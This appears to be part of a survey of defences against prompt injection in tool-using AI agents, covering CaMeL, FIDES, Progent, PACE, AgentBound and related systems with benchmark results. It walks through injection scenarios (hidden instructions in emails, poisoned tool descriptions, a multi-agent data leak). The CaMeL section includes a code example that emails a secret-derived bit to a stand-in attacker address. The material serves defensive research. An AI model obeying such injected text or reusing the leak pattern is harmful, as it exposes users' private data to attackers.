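Li and colleagues ran 1,167 cases with different combinations of PACE's parts, using the model Qwen-3.8-27B, to find out which part is responsible for its results. The full system includes both checks and a component that adapts how PACE responds to calls that fail them. AgentDyn is a newer benchmark that, according to *StepGuard* (2026), emphasises longer tasks, changing plans and helpful instructions from third parties.

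| Parts switched on | AgentDojo: attacks succeeding | AgentDojo: tasks completed | AgentDyn: attacks succeeding | AgentDyn: tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Data-flow check only | 0.0% | 13.6% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Effect check only | 0.0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
| Full system | 0.0% | 67.2% | 0.0% | 33.3% |

The effect check alone stopped nearly all the attacks and left the agent far more useful than the data-flow check did. But the full system still halved the number of tasks completed on AgentDyn. This conflicts with the paper's main result, that PACE lowers task completion by at most three points on full benchmarks. Li and colleagues attribute the difference to the mix of tasks in the smaller sample, so the loss in practice depends heavily on what users ask for.

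Li and colleagues also searched for attacks that adapt to PACE. On 30 pairs of tasks and attacks from AgentDojo, the search succeeded 21 times against the undefended agent and never against PACE. With so few pairs, the true success rate against PACE could still be as high as 11%. The paper's proofs don't rule out successful attacks on the tested version either, because they cover a stricter one. The tested version can restore a call that the data-flow check blocked, provided the effect check accepts it, and can run a repaired call without checking its effects again.

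AgentDojo results for Progent, AgentCap and PACE are hard to compare directly:

| System and agent model | Tested by | Attacks succeeding, before and after | Tasks completed, before and after |
|---|---|---|---|
| Progent, GPT-4o | Shi, He and colleagues | 39.9%, 1.0% | Little change |
| Progent, GPT-4o | Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao | 45.6%, about 5% | 73.6%, 59.6% |
| Progent, Qwen2.5-7B | Narisetty and colleagues | 25.8%, 4.2% | 45.2%, 27.1% |
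| AgentCap, GPT-4o | Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao | 45.6%, 5.1% | 73.6%, 74.9% |
| AgentCap, GPT-5.4 | Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao | 33.2%, 0.0% | 75.7%, 75.0% |
| PACE, Qwen-3.8-27B | Li and colleagues | 48.0%, 0.0% | 62.6%, 59.7% |
| PACE, GPT-5.6 Luna | Li and colleagues | 100.0%, 8.1% | 73.8%, 72.1% |

The PACE rows show the most successful group of attacks for each model, so their initial attack success rates are high. Narisetty and colleagues used only part of the benchmark, and Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao used a later version with 949 cases. Despite these differences, attack success fell sharply in every test, while the effect on usefulness varied from almost nothing to a loss of 18 points.

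### Lingering Authority: permission that ends with the subtask

A permission can be right for one step and dangerous later. ChatGPT's remembered approvals have this problem, because approval to write to Maria lasts for the rest of the conversation. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) presents PORTICO, a system that revokes each permission a coding agent holds once it is no longer needed.

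In one example, the agent has to add a timeout setting to a program. It starts with access to one source file and its tests. The task's written contract allows the agent to request a second file, so PORTICO grants the request by issuing a handle, a temporary reference that works only for that file. The handle stops working when the tests pass. The model can't extend the permission by writing that it needs more time, or regain it by using the file's name. Only trusted events determine whether the permission lasts, such as a test run that PORTICO started itself or a decision by an authenticated person.

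Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same permissions at the same times but never withdrew them. Both completed the task in all ten runs. The agent then tried to read one file again, and PORTICO refused every time while the other version allowed it every time. In six more cases, a model received a malicious instruction to reuse an old permission to write a file, alter a code repository or contact an outside machine. PORTICO blocked all six attempts, and the version without revocation carried out all six. These results confirm that the code works as designed, but they don't estimate how often real agents misuse old permissions.

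Agents completed fewer tasks under tighter permissions. Across 37 coding tasks with five runs each, agents limited to their initial permissions completed 21%. Letting them request more raised this to 87%, compared with 97% for a fixed list of permitted tools and paths. In separate runs on real software projects, agents completed 31 of 42 tasks under PORTICO and all 42 when permissions lasted for the whole task. Some contracts ended a permission too early or gave the agent no way to get it back.

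PORTICO recorded no violations of its contracts in the main experiments, but Santos-Grueiro used the same contracts to enforce the limits and to count violations. If a contract permits an action it shouldn't, PORTICO allows the action and it isn't counted as a violation. Santos-Grueiro did not measure how long the contracts take to write.

### Who writes the policy

All these gates depend on a correct policy, and a vague request makes the policy much harder to get right. If the user of the office assistant types "Sort out the caterer," they could mean answering an email, paying an invoice or cancelling the order.

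An operator who writes rules in advance doesn't know what the user will request, so the rules have to permit everything the assistant might legitimately do, perhaps mail to any known contact and payments to any approved supplier. A vague request doesn't weaken these rules, and injected text can't alter them. But they don't separate the actions this user wants from the others they permit. If an injected email leads the agent to cancel the order, or to send one supplier's prices to another, every call may satisfy the rules.

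*Runtime Authorization Consistency Checking for MCP-based Agentic Workflows* (Zhang, Lee and colleagues, 2026) describes a similar problem that can arise without an attack. A user asks an assistant to find free slots in a calendar and not to read mail or contact anyone. The assistant has standing permission to use mail, so it searches for context, notices a conflict and sends a message to reschedule a meeting. Each call is permitted, but together they go beyond the request. The paper's system compares each new call with the authority that earlier accepted steps have passed on. On plans that language models wrote without knowing the rules, it blocked 92.8% of the steps it should have, compared with 68.8% for the best simpler check. However, it doesn't turn a request such as "Sort out the caterer" into the precise session grant it starts from, so another component has to supply that grant.

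A model that derives rules from the request can make them more specific. For "summarise the morning's mail", it can permit search_mail but not send_mail. If the request is vague, the rules may be too narrow for the agent to pay a genuine invoice, or broad enough to permit payments the user never wanted. Shi, He and colleagues acknowledge that an ambiguous task can lead Progent to permit more than necessary.

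If the model refines its guess as the work proceeds, it does so after reading mail, so the attacker's text can influence the decision. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent's updates may loosen the rules in response to an adversarial tool result, and that people make mistakes when they write such policies by hand. Progent's solver detects the loosening, so the first objection applies mainly when approval is automatic or careless, but somebody still has to decide whether to approve. Refusing every expansion would leave Alice's to-do list undone. Asking the user brings back the approval prompts that people in Yan's experiment often accepted when they shouldn't have.

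Narisetty and colleagues consider the deepest open problem for such defences to be tasks in which the user wants a stranger's text to determine what the agent does. Their example is a request to read an email and add a meeting to the calendar if the email proposes one. No policy can make the email's text trustworthy, but a policy can limit the consequences, for instance by allowing a new calendar entry but no invitations to other people.

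In the most promising arrangement, the operator sets outer limits that no request can override, such as approved bank accounts, and a model narrows the permissions within those limits for each task. Progent supports this with fixed rules that take priority over the generated ones. If the model chooses the wrong permissions, it can do no more damage than the operator's rules allow, although it can still make the agent less useful. When a request is too vague for the model to choose sensible permissions, the host should ask the user to clarify before the agent reads any outside text.

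### What these checks take on trust

Let E(c) be the effects that the gate's schema or catalogue assigns to a tool call c, and let P be the set of permitted effects. The gate ensures that E(c) ⊆ P. The call is safe if its actual effects A also satisfy A ⊆ E(c), but the gate does not establish this. A gate that uses annotations has the same gap. Although E(c) is still only a description of the code, it is more precise than an annotation because it depends on the arguments, and it can be more reliable if the operator writes the catalogue instead of the server's author.

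Mellafe Zuvic trusts the tools, and other researchers make much the same assumption. Santos-Grueiro assumes that the catalogue correctly maps each call to its effects, and Zhang and colleagues exclude hidden side effects. Li and colleagues' guarantee does not cover tools that make hidden secondary calls.

A policy that checks each call can also depend on labels describing the tools. In the AgentDojo tests of Progent, Shi, He and colleagues permitted non-sensitive read-only tools for every task. The tested version of PACE can release a call that the request didn't authorise if the schema marks all its effects as reversible and none as lasting or sending anything out. The researchers prepared these classifications themselves. An operator with hundreds of third-party tools might base them on readOnlyHint, and a false hint would then exempt the tool from much of the check.

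A dishonest tool may also influence a policy that a model writes. Progent's policy-writing model reads the user's request and the available tools' definitions. Shi, He and colleagues treat both as trusted, although a server's author controls the definitions. Li and colleagues tested Progent on MCPTox, a benchmark of poisoned tool descriptions. Between 8.8% and 46.4% of attacks succeeded, depending on the agent's model, compared with 32.5% to 86.9% without a defence. PACE, which derives authority only from the authenticated request, kept attack success below 3%. A gate can stop these attacks because a poisoned description causes harm by making the model propose a bad call, often to an honest tool.

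In the first variant of the office assistant example, the user wants a summary of the morning's mail, but injected text makes the model propose sending invoices to an outside address. A gate like ScopeGate refuses the call if the operator has limited send_mail to colleagues. Progent should refuse it because a summary requires no outgoing mail, unless the policy-writing model proposes adding send_mail and someone approves. AgentCap refuses it if the policy protects the recipient argument, because the address appears only in untrusted text. These decisions stay the same however persuasive the agent finds the injected message.

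A different injection could still succeed. Suppose the user asks the agent to email Maria the caterer's price, and the hidden text contains an instruction to include everyone's salaries in the same message. The tool and the recipient are correct, and a list of approved values can't usefully restrict the body of an email because it is free text.

In the second variant, search_mail forwards what it finds. The request clearly calls for a search, so ScopeGate, Progent, AgentCap and PACE would all allow the call under reasonable policies, and the tool would forward the mail after their checks had finished. A stricter policy on arguments would not help, because the search_mail server can already read the mailbox and doesn't need the model to pass it anything secret. Such a policy can only limit what the model passes to a tool, so it could have kept the private key out of the note field in Invariant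 Labs' addition tool.

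## Experiments that track where data came from

Data-flow tracking records where each value the agent handles came from and who may read it. A host needs this information to keep injected text from adding everyone's salaries to a message for Maria.

The best-known system of this kind is CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). The paper later appeared at the SaTML 2026 conference.

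### How CaMeL runs a request

CaMeL builds on a design with two language models that Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model plans the tool calls and never sees what the tools return. A quarantined model reads the returned content but can't call tools. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains a flaw that the CaMeL researchers found in his design. If the user asks the agent to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in the meeting notes, the quarantined model has to extract the address. Text hidden in the notes can make it return the attacker's address instead, so the agent follows the original plan but sends the document to the attacker.

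CaMeL therefore adds an interpreter, an ordinary program that runs the plan, labels every value and checks the labels before each call. Suppose the user picks Maria from a contact list and types, "Find the caterer's invoice and tell Maria the amount." The privileged model reads the request and the tool definitions, then writes the whole plan in a restricted form of Python:

```python
mails  = search_mail("caterer invoice")
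amount = quarantined_model("Find the invoice total", mails, output=float)
send_mail(to="maria@example.com", body="The invoice is for " + str(amount))
```

The interpreter runs the first line and stores the messages as `mails`, without showing them to the privileged model. On the second line, it passes them to the quarantined model, which must return a number.

As Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLoT*, each value's labels record its sources and its permitted readers. When a program makes a value z from x and y, the usual rule for combining such labels is

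sources(z) = sources(x) ∪ sources(y)

readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y).

If only the people on an email may read it, the example produces these labels:

| Value | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| Maria's address | The user | Anyone |
| mails | The caterer, through search_mail | The user and the caterer |
| amount | The caterer, through search_mail | The user and the caterer |
| Body of the message | The privileged model's plan and the caterer | The user and the caterer |

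Before each call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that receives the tool's name, the arguments and their labels, and allows or refuses the call. A policy might always allow searches, but allow send_mail only if the address comes from a trusted source and the recipient may read the body. Maria's address passes, but the body fails because she was not a recipient of the caterer's email, even though the user asked for this message. The host can then ask the user to approve the call, or the operator can relax the rule for recipients the user has chosen.

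If the user asks only for a summary of the morning's mail, CaMeL's plan contains a search and a summary but no call to send_mail. A hidden instruction to send invoices to a stranger can distort the summary, but it can't cause the invoices to be sent, even without a policy.

The attempt to add salaries to Maria's message also fails here, because the quarantined model can return only a number. If the plan allowed free text, the model could copy salaries from any email the search found. A strict policy would still block sending the salaries to Maria, but the relaxed rule for chosen recipients would allow it.

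### Labels rather than references

CaMeL is short for "capabilities for machine learning", but its capabilities are labels on values, not capabilities in Hardy's or Miller's sense. Policies use these labels to decide whether to allow a tool call, but the labels themselves grant no access. The plan may name any tool the host offers, so a badly written policy can let a harmful call through. With object capabilities, a program without a reference to a tool can't call it, whatever the policy.

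A model can't forge a reference or a label by writing text, and both distinguish requests that an access list would treat the same. For example, a CaMeL policy can check sources(address) to accept an address the user chose but reject the same address if it came from an email.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) stays closer to the older meaning. Its agents write programs in Scala 3, and the compiler tracks which capabilities each piece of code uses. *LACUNA* (2026) uses the same compiler feature to ensure that the model's code can call a tool only where the tool's capability is in scope. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) report that TACIT, a Scala system by Odersky and colleagues, resisted all but one of 1,926 attacks in the AgentDojo benchmark. They attribute the exception to the benchmark's scoring, which counted a quoted hotel review as a successful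 attack.

### What CaMeL guarantees

Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, define the guarantee precisely. Let u be the user's request and t the trusted information about the tools and their environment. The privileged model produces a plan π from u and t alone. CaMeL is then supposed to ensure two things:

- **Control flow:** the agent makes only calls that π contains. Untrusted data can affect which of π's existing branches runs, but it can't add a call.
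- **Data flow:** every call satisfies the policy, so no value reaches a recipient that the policy forbids for a value with those labels.

Neither part depends on the quarantined model resisting the attack. However, the guarantee doesn't cover whether the values are correct, so in the example, a misleading email could still make the agent send Maria the wrong amount.

*Architecting Secure AI Agents* (2026) describes a similar limit in CaMeL's policy for a payment tool. The policy permits a payment only if the recipient comes solely from the user and is allowed to see all the payment's details. Like AgentCap's rule, it blocks even a genuine payment if the account number comes from an email. If the user supplies the number, the money goes to the right account, but injected text can still raise the amount.

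Attackers can also exploit branches within a plan. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) applies the design to agents that operate a computer through its screen, where a plan has to include branches for what might appear. A fake button can lead the agent into a branch that is valid but dangerous. *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) confirms that trusted planning alone doesn't prevent this and tests constraints on individual branches.

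### Leaks in the tracking

Garby and colleagues found cases in which CaMeL loses track of a secret. They describe a program that reveals whether a bank balance exceeds some threshold, which might look like this:

```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the program changes tmp and therefore skips the line that sets rich to False. CaMeL updates a variable's label only when it runs a line that changes the variable. So rich keeps its public label even though its value reveals the secret, and the email goes out.

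CaMeL can also leak data because it retries failed plans in a loop outside the interpreter. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and repeated attempts could reveal all of it.

An attacker who can only plant text in an email doesn't write the plan, so exploiting these leaks would require a careless or compromised planner. A bug that Garby and colleagues mention in a footnote seems more likely to matter in practice. When a program inserts an untrusted value into a text template, CaMeL treats the result as trusted. Ordinary plans do this often, for example to put an invoice amount in a message. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) had warned that strong guarantees about information flow are difficult in Python, and recommended a language designed for the purpose.

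CaMeL's guarantee can also fail when several agents work together, even if each runs CaMeL. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system in which one agent queried a database of job applicants, another sent notifications and a third coordinated them. The user asked the system to send Julie a summary on Slack. A hidden instruction in the database passed through the first two steps as untrusted data. The coordinator then put the summary into its written request to the notification agent, which treated the whole request as coming from its user. That agent planned an extra email and sent the applicants' data to an outside address.

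Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that, under mild assumptions about what users can request, any such hierarchy of two or more agents with an untrusted data source can fail in this way. Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, makes agents pass instructions and untrusted values through separate channels. Across five models on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and never with multi-CaMeL.

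### Tasks that can't be planned in advance

CaMeL has to write its plan before it reads anything, which rules out some ordinary requests. If the user types "Do what Alice's email asks", the privileged model can't plan the tool calls, because they depend on the email's contents.

In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) tested CaMeL with four models on 60 tasks of this kind in shopping, software development and daily life. CaMeL completed none of the tasks with any model. Without a defence, three of the models completed between 52% and 60%. No attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but this is little evidence that it is secure, because it also completed no tasks.

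These tasks were designed to be hard to complete with a fixed plan, and most requests may well be easier. AgentDojo contains few such tasks, though the number depends on the definition. *Trident* (2026) counts 20 of its 97 tasks as data-dependent, while the AgentDyn researchers count only six that need dynamic planning. Much of the difference may be tasks for which a planner can write the alternatives in advance, such as "if the invoice is overdue, remind me". By either count, AgentDojo results probably understate how much usefulness an agent would lose under CaMeL for a user who often delegates open-ended work.

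### The cost in completed tasks

The revised CaMeL paper reports that CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo's tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. The loss can be much larger with a weaker model. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues, 2025) quotes CaMeL's published result with GPT-4o as 53.6%, while undefended GPT-4o completed 83.0% of tasks in the paper's own test. CaMeL also needs 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens for the median task.

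Under attack, however, CaMeL completed more tasks than undefended GPT-4o (54.5% versus 50.0%), probably because injections also divert an undefended agent from its task.

Part of the loss in task completion comes from having to plan without seeing any data. Peters-Gill and colleagues isolated this effect by running CaMeL with no policies on AssetOpsBench, a set of professional tasks for teams of agents. Giving each agent CaMeL lowered task completion by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by only 13.4 points for the two strongest models, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Multi-CaMeL lowered it by another 3.2 points on average and by less than one point for those two. Better models should therefore reduce this loss further, although they can't base a plan on information they haven't seen.

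Policies add a cost of their own. Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each:

| Model | Tasks completed, policies off | Tasks completed, policies on |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 37.5% |

With so few tasks, the margins of error are wide, but the loss is large for both models. In return, the policies cut successful attacks from 5 of 622 to none of 588. The fixed plan was usually enough to stop an attack on its own, because in about two thirds of the task and attack pairings the attacker needed a call that would never appear in the plan. An attacker who knew that the policies were off would presumably target the arguments of planned calls instead, so these figures don't show that an operator can safely do without the policies.

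AgentDojo results alone may not justify CaMeL's complexity, because a simpler defence also reduced successful attacks to zero. Bhagwatkar and colleagues used a second model to remove suspicious instructions from tool results, and GPT-4o completed 74.1% of the tasks with this defence in place. They conclude that the benchmark's attacks are too weak. Their filter has to recognise each attack, whereas CaMeL's fixed plan works against attacks nobody has thought of yet.

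### Reducing the cost

One way to recover lost tasks is to specify in the plan which data to trust. Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, LLMbda, in which every value has a label, and used the proof checker Lean to prove that its tracking is sound. Their agent, RANDORI, can "endorse" a value, or mark it as trusted despite its source. The model writes these endorsements into the plan before reading any outside content, so injected text can't prompt it to add one.

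With GPT-5.2, RANDORI completed 75% of the banking tasks with its checks always on, twice the rate of CaMeL with its policies on. Across three models, only two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user made the same request, to read a file and pay as it instructed, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without endorsement, the checks blocked this attack, but the share of tasks completed with Qwen3.7-plus fell from 75% to 62.5%. No rule based on sources can distinguish the genuine bill from the attacker's in this case, because both arrive in the file the user chose to trust.

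CaMeL checks a policy only when the plan reaches the tool call, so a plan may do a lot of work before a forbidden last step. Nikolaou and colleagues extend CaMeL to check the entire plan before running any of it. If the plan could break a rule, the check returns an example of how, and the privileged model writes another plan. The check treats loops cautiously, so it may reject some safe plans.

Microsoft's FIDES, described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025), is more flexible and lets the planner choose its calls one at a time. If a tool returns data that is less trusted than the planner's context, FIDES hides the data in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner can pass the variable to another tool, ask a quarantined model about it or open it. Opening it makes the context untrusted, and from then on the policy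 blocks calls with serious consequences.

Suppose a user asks the agent to create a calendar entry if any of the morning's emails proposes a meeting. In FIDES, the quarantined model can answer yes or no, and the policy can allow the planner to act on that one bit. If the answer is yes, the planner has the quarantined model extract the time and place into another variable, which goes straight to the calendar tool. An attacker could cause a false calendar entry but could not make the agent email a stranger. Costa and colleagues left this one-bit feature out of their experiments because few AgentDojo tasks needed it.

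On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against a basic agent and none succeeded against FIDES with its policies on. Without attacks, the share of tasks completed, counting every task equally, fell from about 82% with the basic agent to 52% with FIDES, almost the same loss as CaMeL's with that model. With the reasoning model o1, FIDES came closer to completing all the tasks its policies allow. FIDES's guarantee covers only direct flows of data, so an observer could still learn something from the order or timing of the agent's calls.

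Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, argue that such comparisons are unfair to data-flow tracking. In practice, many undefended agents ask a person before every consequential action, so Kolluri and colleagues count approvals as a cost too. They also built Prudentia, a version of FIDES whose planner knows the policies and tries to avoid breaking them. With the model o3-mini, the results on AgentDojo were:

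| Agent | Tasks completed without any approval | Approvals needed over all completed tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential call | 24.3% | 48.2 |
| Same agent with data-flow tracking | 35.5% | 32.4 |
| FIDES | 50.1% | 18.8 |
| Prudentia | 59.1% | About 17 |

By this measure, tracking makes agents more useful, because the policy can approve calls that a person would otherwise have to check.

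The remaining approvals need more care, though. Prudentia can ask the user to endorse a whole email instead of approving each action that follows from it, so a to-do list with ten items takes one approval instead of ten. But if someone has hidden an eleventh item in the email, the user has to notice it in the text, because no later prompt will show that action separately. Kolluri and colleagues count approvals but don't test how well people judge them, and the experiments by Anthropic and Yan suggest that people would often approve the wrong thing.

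### Who describes the tools

All these systems depend on descriptions of the tools. For each tool f, FIDES needs the set R(f) of data that f may read and the set W(f) of data that f may change. The tool's result inherits every restriction on the data in R(f), on the call and on its arguments. FIDES also needs to know which calls have serious consequences, which send data out and who will receive it. These facts make up D, the tool's declared effects, and are more detailed than MCP's four hints. The guarantee holds only if A ⊆ D.

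CaMeL also needs the format of each tool's results, because the privileged model writes code to process the results without seeing them. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add these formats to the tool descriptions in both of their benchmarks. A mistake in a format usually makes the plan fail, but a mistake about what a tool discloses can cause a leak.

In the experiments, the researchers themselves specified which data could be trusted. Costa and colleagues labelled a field untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it, so their labels covered every place where an attack could appear. Real operators don't have a list of those places. *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026) describes a test of CaMeL in which the researchers had to write the policies and decide field by field which tool results to trust. CaMeL completed only 13% to 14% of the tasks in that test. Willison welcomed CaMeL as the first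 credible defence of its kind, but he is nervous about any system that requires users to think about security policies, because he finds them hard to write himself.

An operator can reduce the risk by treating all results from an unfamiliar tool as untrusted and private. This protects against a server that wrongly marks its output as safe, but not against a search_mail tool that secretly forwards what it finds, because CaMeL and FIDES track data between tools, not inside them. Kolluri and colleagues assume that every tool's code is trustworthy.

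A dishonest description can also corrupt the plan. The privileged model treats tool definitions as trusted, so it might act on a false statement like the one in Invariant Labs' experiment that all email must go to a certain address. It would then write the attacker's address into the program. In Nikolaou and colleagues' system, anything written directly into the program counts as trusted, so the address would pass a check on its source. Costa and colleagues exclude this attack by assuming that tool descriptions are honest.

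## Confining the tool itself

Confinement restricts the code inside each tool, which CaMeL and FIDES assume is trustworthy. An operator who confines a tool no longer has to trust its author, but does have to trust whatever enforces the restrictions.

### What enforces each limit

An MCP server on the user's machine usually runs as a process with all the user's rights. An operating-system sandbox removes most of those rights. The kernel, the core of the operating system, handles every request to open a file or a network connection and blocks those the sandbox's rules don't allow. A container, such as Docker's, also gives the process its own file system, which includes only selected folders from the real one.

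WebAssembly is a format for compiled programs that can reach the outside world only through functions their runtime supplies. WASI, the standard set of such functions, gives a program no ambient authority, so the host has to grant access to each file or connection. Of the limits described here, this is the closest to Miller's object capabilities.

The other limits apply further from the tool's code. A network allowlist restricts which addresses a process can contact. A read-only database account makes the database reject every write, which would have stopped the query that bypassed the read-only mode of Anthropic's PostgreSQL server. A scoped credential is a token that an online service accepts only for certain operations or resources. For example, the software vendor Abyssale checks every call to its MCP tools against both the scope the user approved for the client and the user's role in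 the account.

| Limit | What enforces it | What the operator must trust |
|---|---|---|
| Operating-system sandbox or container | The kernel | The kernel, the sandbox software and the choice of folders |
| WebAssembly component | The WebAssembly runtime | The runtime and the functions it supplies |
| Network allowlist | A firewall or proxy outside the tool's process | The firewall and every permitted destination |
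| Read-only database account | The database | The database and the rights set for the account |
| Scoped credential | The service that accepts it | The service, and that the tool can't find a broader credential |

One tool often needs more than one kind of confinement. A sandbox can keep search_mail away from the user's private keys, but if the mailbox is on a remote server, reading a message and deleting one both produce encrypted traffic to the same address. Only the mail service can distinguish them, so preventing deletion requires a read-only credential.

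### AgentBound

Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues (2025), in *AgentBound*, built a system that confines existing MCP servers without changing their code. Each server comes with a manifest, a file that lists the kinds of access it needs, such as reading files, reading environment variables (settings that often hold passwords) or making outgoing connections. For search_mail, a simplified manifest might be:

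```json
{
  "description": "Finds messages in the user's mailbox",
  "permissions": ["network.client", "system.env.read"]
}
```

When the server starts, the user fills in the details, in this case the mail provider's address and the variable that holds the mailbox password. AgentBound then runs the server in a Docker container with access to only the approved folders, variables and network addresses. If the agent tries to add a kind of access that the manifest doesn't list, AgentBound aborts the run.

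Bühler and colleagues first tried a server written to steal a private login key. Without confinement, it sent the key out. With the network blocked, it could read the key but not send it. With the file system restricted too, it couldn't read the key.

The testers then ran AgentBound against 14 malicious or vulnerable servers from two public collections. It stopped the attacks on eight and failed on five. The last server combined several attacks, and AgentBound could stop only some of them. One success was a Google Maps server whose code secretly switched to a different address, a clear case of a misdescribed tool. One failure was a clock server whose description told the model to redirect cryptocurrency transfers made through another server. AgentBound didn't stop this attack because the clock server stayed within its permissions and the transfer tool contacted a service it was allowed to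 use. The testers wrote or checked the manifests themselves, so the results show what confinement can do with suitable permissions.

The container adds little delay. In the published measurements, it added about 90 to 430 milliseconds to a server's startup and less than a millisecond to each operation.

Writing correct manifests is harder, because a server will break if its manifest omits something it needs. Bühler and colleagues had language models write manifests for 296 popular servers and asked the developers of 96 of them to check the results. They report 80.9% accuracy, which corresponds to 17 acceptances and four rejections. Most developers never replied.

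In a closer comparison, the generated manifests exactly matched those written by people for 28 of 48 servers. The other 20 had 29 differences in total. In 23 of these, the model left out a permission that the person had included, and in the other six it added one. The six additions can account for at most six of the 20 servers, so the manifests for at least 14 lacked a permission. If the human versions were right, enforcing the generated manifests unchanged would have broken some function of each of those servers.

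AgentBound also has two gaps in its network limits. It installs the server's package inside the container before it switches on the firewall, so code that runs during installation, as in the fake PostgreSQL package, can still use the network. The firewall filters by IP address, so permitting one site also permits any others that share its address. AgentBound's protection also depends on Docker and the Linux kernel, and an attacker who can exploit a flaw in either could escape the container.

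### How a declaration becomes binding

The manifest is a declaration by the server's author, as an annotation is, but the runtime treats it as a ceiling. Let M be the set of effects that the manifest allows, G the part of M that the user grants, and T the effects that the code attempts. The actual effects are then

A = T ∩ G ⊆ G ⊆ M.

Here M takes the place of D, the declared effects. As long as the runtime controls every route to the outside, A ⊆ D no longer depends on the author's honesty or care. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) formalizes this for skills, which are folders of instructions and scripts that an agent can load. Its sandbox compares every action with the skill's declared capabilities and denies anything outside them.

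This changes what happens when a declaration is wrong:

| Error | With an annotation | With an enforced manifest |
|---|---|---|
| The author leaves out something the tool does | The host may skip a check, and the tool does it anyway | The operation fails |
| The author lists more than the tool needs | The user sees unnecessary prompts | The user can refuse the excess, but if they grant it, the tool can misuse it |

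A read-only annotation doesn't stop the author of search_mail from forwarding messages to an outside machine. With an enforced manifest, the author has to list outgoing connections and get the user to approve that machine's address. The user might still agree, but the author can no longer hide the connection behind a false declaration.

Developers may also make different mistakes when declarations are binding. *Beyond Maliciousness* (Pandey, Singh and colleagues, 2026) examined 6,309 skills from two marketplaces. A skill's author can list tools that the agent may use without asking, but the list doesn't restrict the skill to those tools. Of the 770 skills with such a list, 59% left out something that their contents could do, and 39% listed something they didn't need. Studies of Android apps and browser extensions had mainly found unneeded permissions. Pandey and colleagues attribute the difference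 to enforcement, because an app can't use a permission it hasn't requested. This is plausible, although language models inferred what each skill could do, and the company behind the scanner ran the study.

If the explanation is right, binding manifests would lead authors to request more permissions than they need, and somebody would have to refuse the excess. *SkillGuard* (Pan, Sun and colleagues, 2026) measured how far enforced manifests for skills reduce attacks. Its system checks each action against the skill's manifest and asks the user about sensitive permissions. On a benchmark of malicious instructions hidden in skills, the system cut the attack success rate from 36.7% to 18.0% for obvious instructions and from 35.3% to 20.7% for ones that blended in with the skill's purpose. It used 24.7% more tokens on average, and agents completed slightly fewer tasks in one of the three hosts tested.

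About half the attacks that had succeeded therefore still worked. Pan and colleagues found that some permissions were too coarse and that high-risk ones needed lists of allowed values. SkillGuard also relies on a language model to work out which permissions a shell command requires. If the model misses one, the command may run with access that nobody approved, whereas a kernel checks each file when the command tries to open it.

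A manifest doesn't have to be binding, though. *Permission Manifests for Web Agents* (2026) proposes a file in which a website lists what visiting agents may do, but deliberately omits enforcement, partly because small sites couldn't afford it. An agent can therefore ignore the file, much as a tool whose readOnlyHint is set to true can still make changes.

### Honest tools that reach too many files

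Confinement can also help when injected text steers the model and the tool has a bug. *My Credentials, Please* (Huang, Tang et al., 2026) describes a flaw in Anthropic's Git server. The server's git_add tool, which stages files (marks them for the next saved version of a project), didn't check that the files were inside the project. Injected text could therefore make the model stage the user's private login key, and a second tool, which shows staged changes, would return the key's contents. A user who approved the calls would have approved two routine Git operations. Anthropic has since fixed the flaw.

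Huang and colleagues looked for similar flaws in other servers and ran three tests on each candidate:

1. Run the attack without a sandbox and check that the tool exposes a planted secret.
2. Run a normal call inside a sandbox and check that it still works.
3. Repeat the attack inside the sandbox and check that the secret stays hidden.

For git_add, the sandbox let the server read and write in the project folder and only read the software it needed. The normal call worked, and the operating system blocked the attempt to open the key.

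A plain file path was enough for the attack in 144 of the 150 confirmed cases. In every case, a sandbox could block a real attack on the tool without breaking the normal call. This doesn't establish how often sandboxing works, because a case was counted only if it passed all three tests. One successful call also doesn't establish that the tool's other functions would still work, and nobody measured how accurate the automatically drafted sandbox rules were.

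The sandbox also wouldn't protect a password saved inside the project folder, since git_add has to read that folder. Huang and colleagues propose adding an fs_scope field to MCP tool definitions, where each tool would declare the files it needs. A client could show this scope to the user and then enforce it.

### Wassette, and who grants the permissions

Microsoft's *Introducing Wassette* (2025) presents an open-source runtime that executes tools as WebAssembly components and offers them to agents through MCP. Microsoft reports using it internally. In the announcement's example, the user asks GitHub Copilot to use a web-fetching tool to summarise a blog post. The tool starts without network access, so Copilot asks the user to let it contact the blog's domain, and then the tool fetches the page.

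Each component has its own policy file. For search_mail, it could contain:

```yaml
permissions:
  network:
    allow:
      - host: "mail.example.com"
  environment:
    allow:
      - key: "MAILBOX_TOKEN"
```

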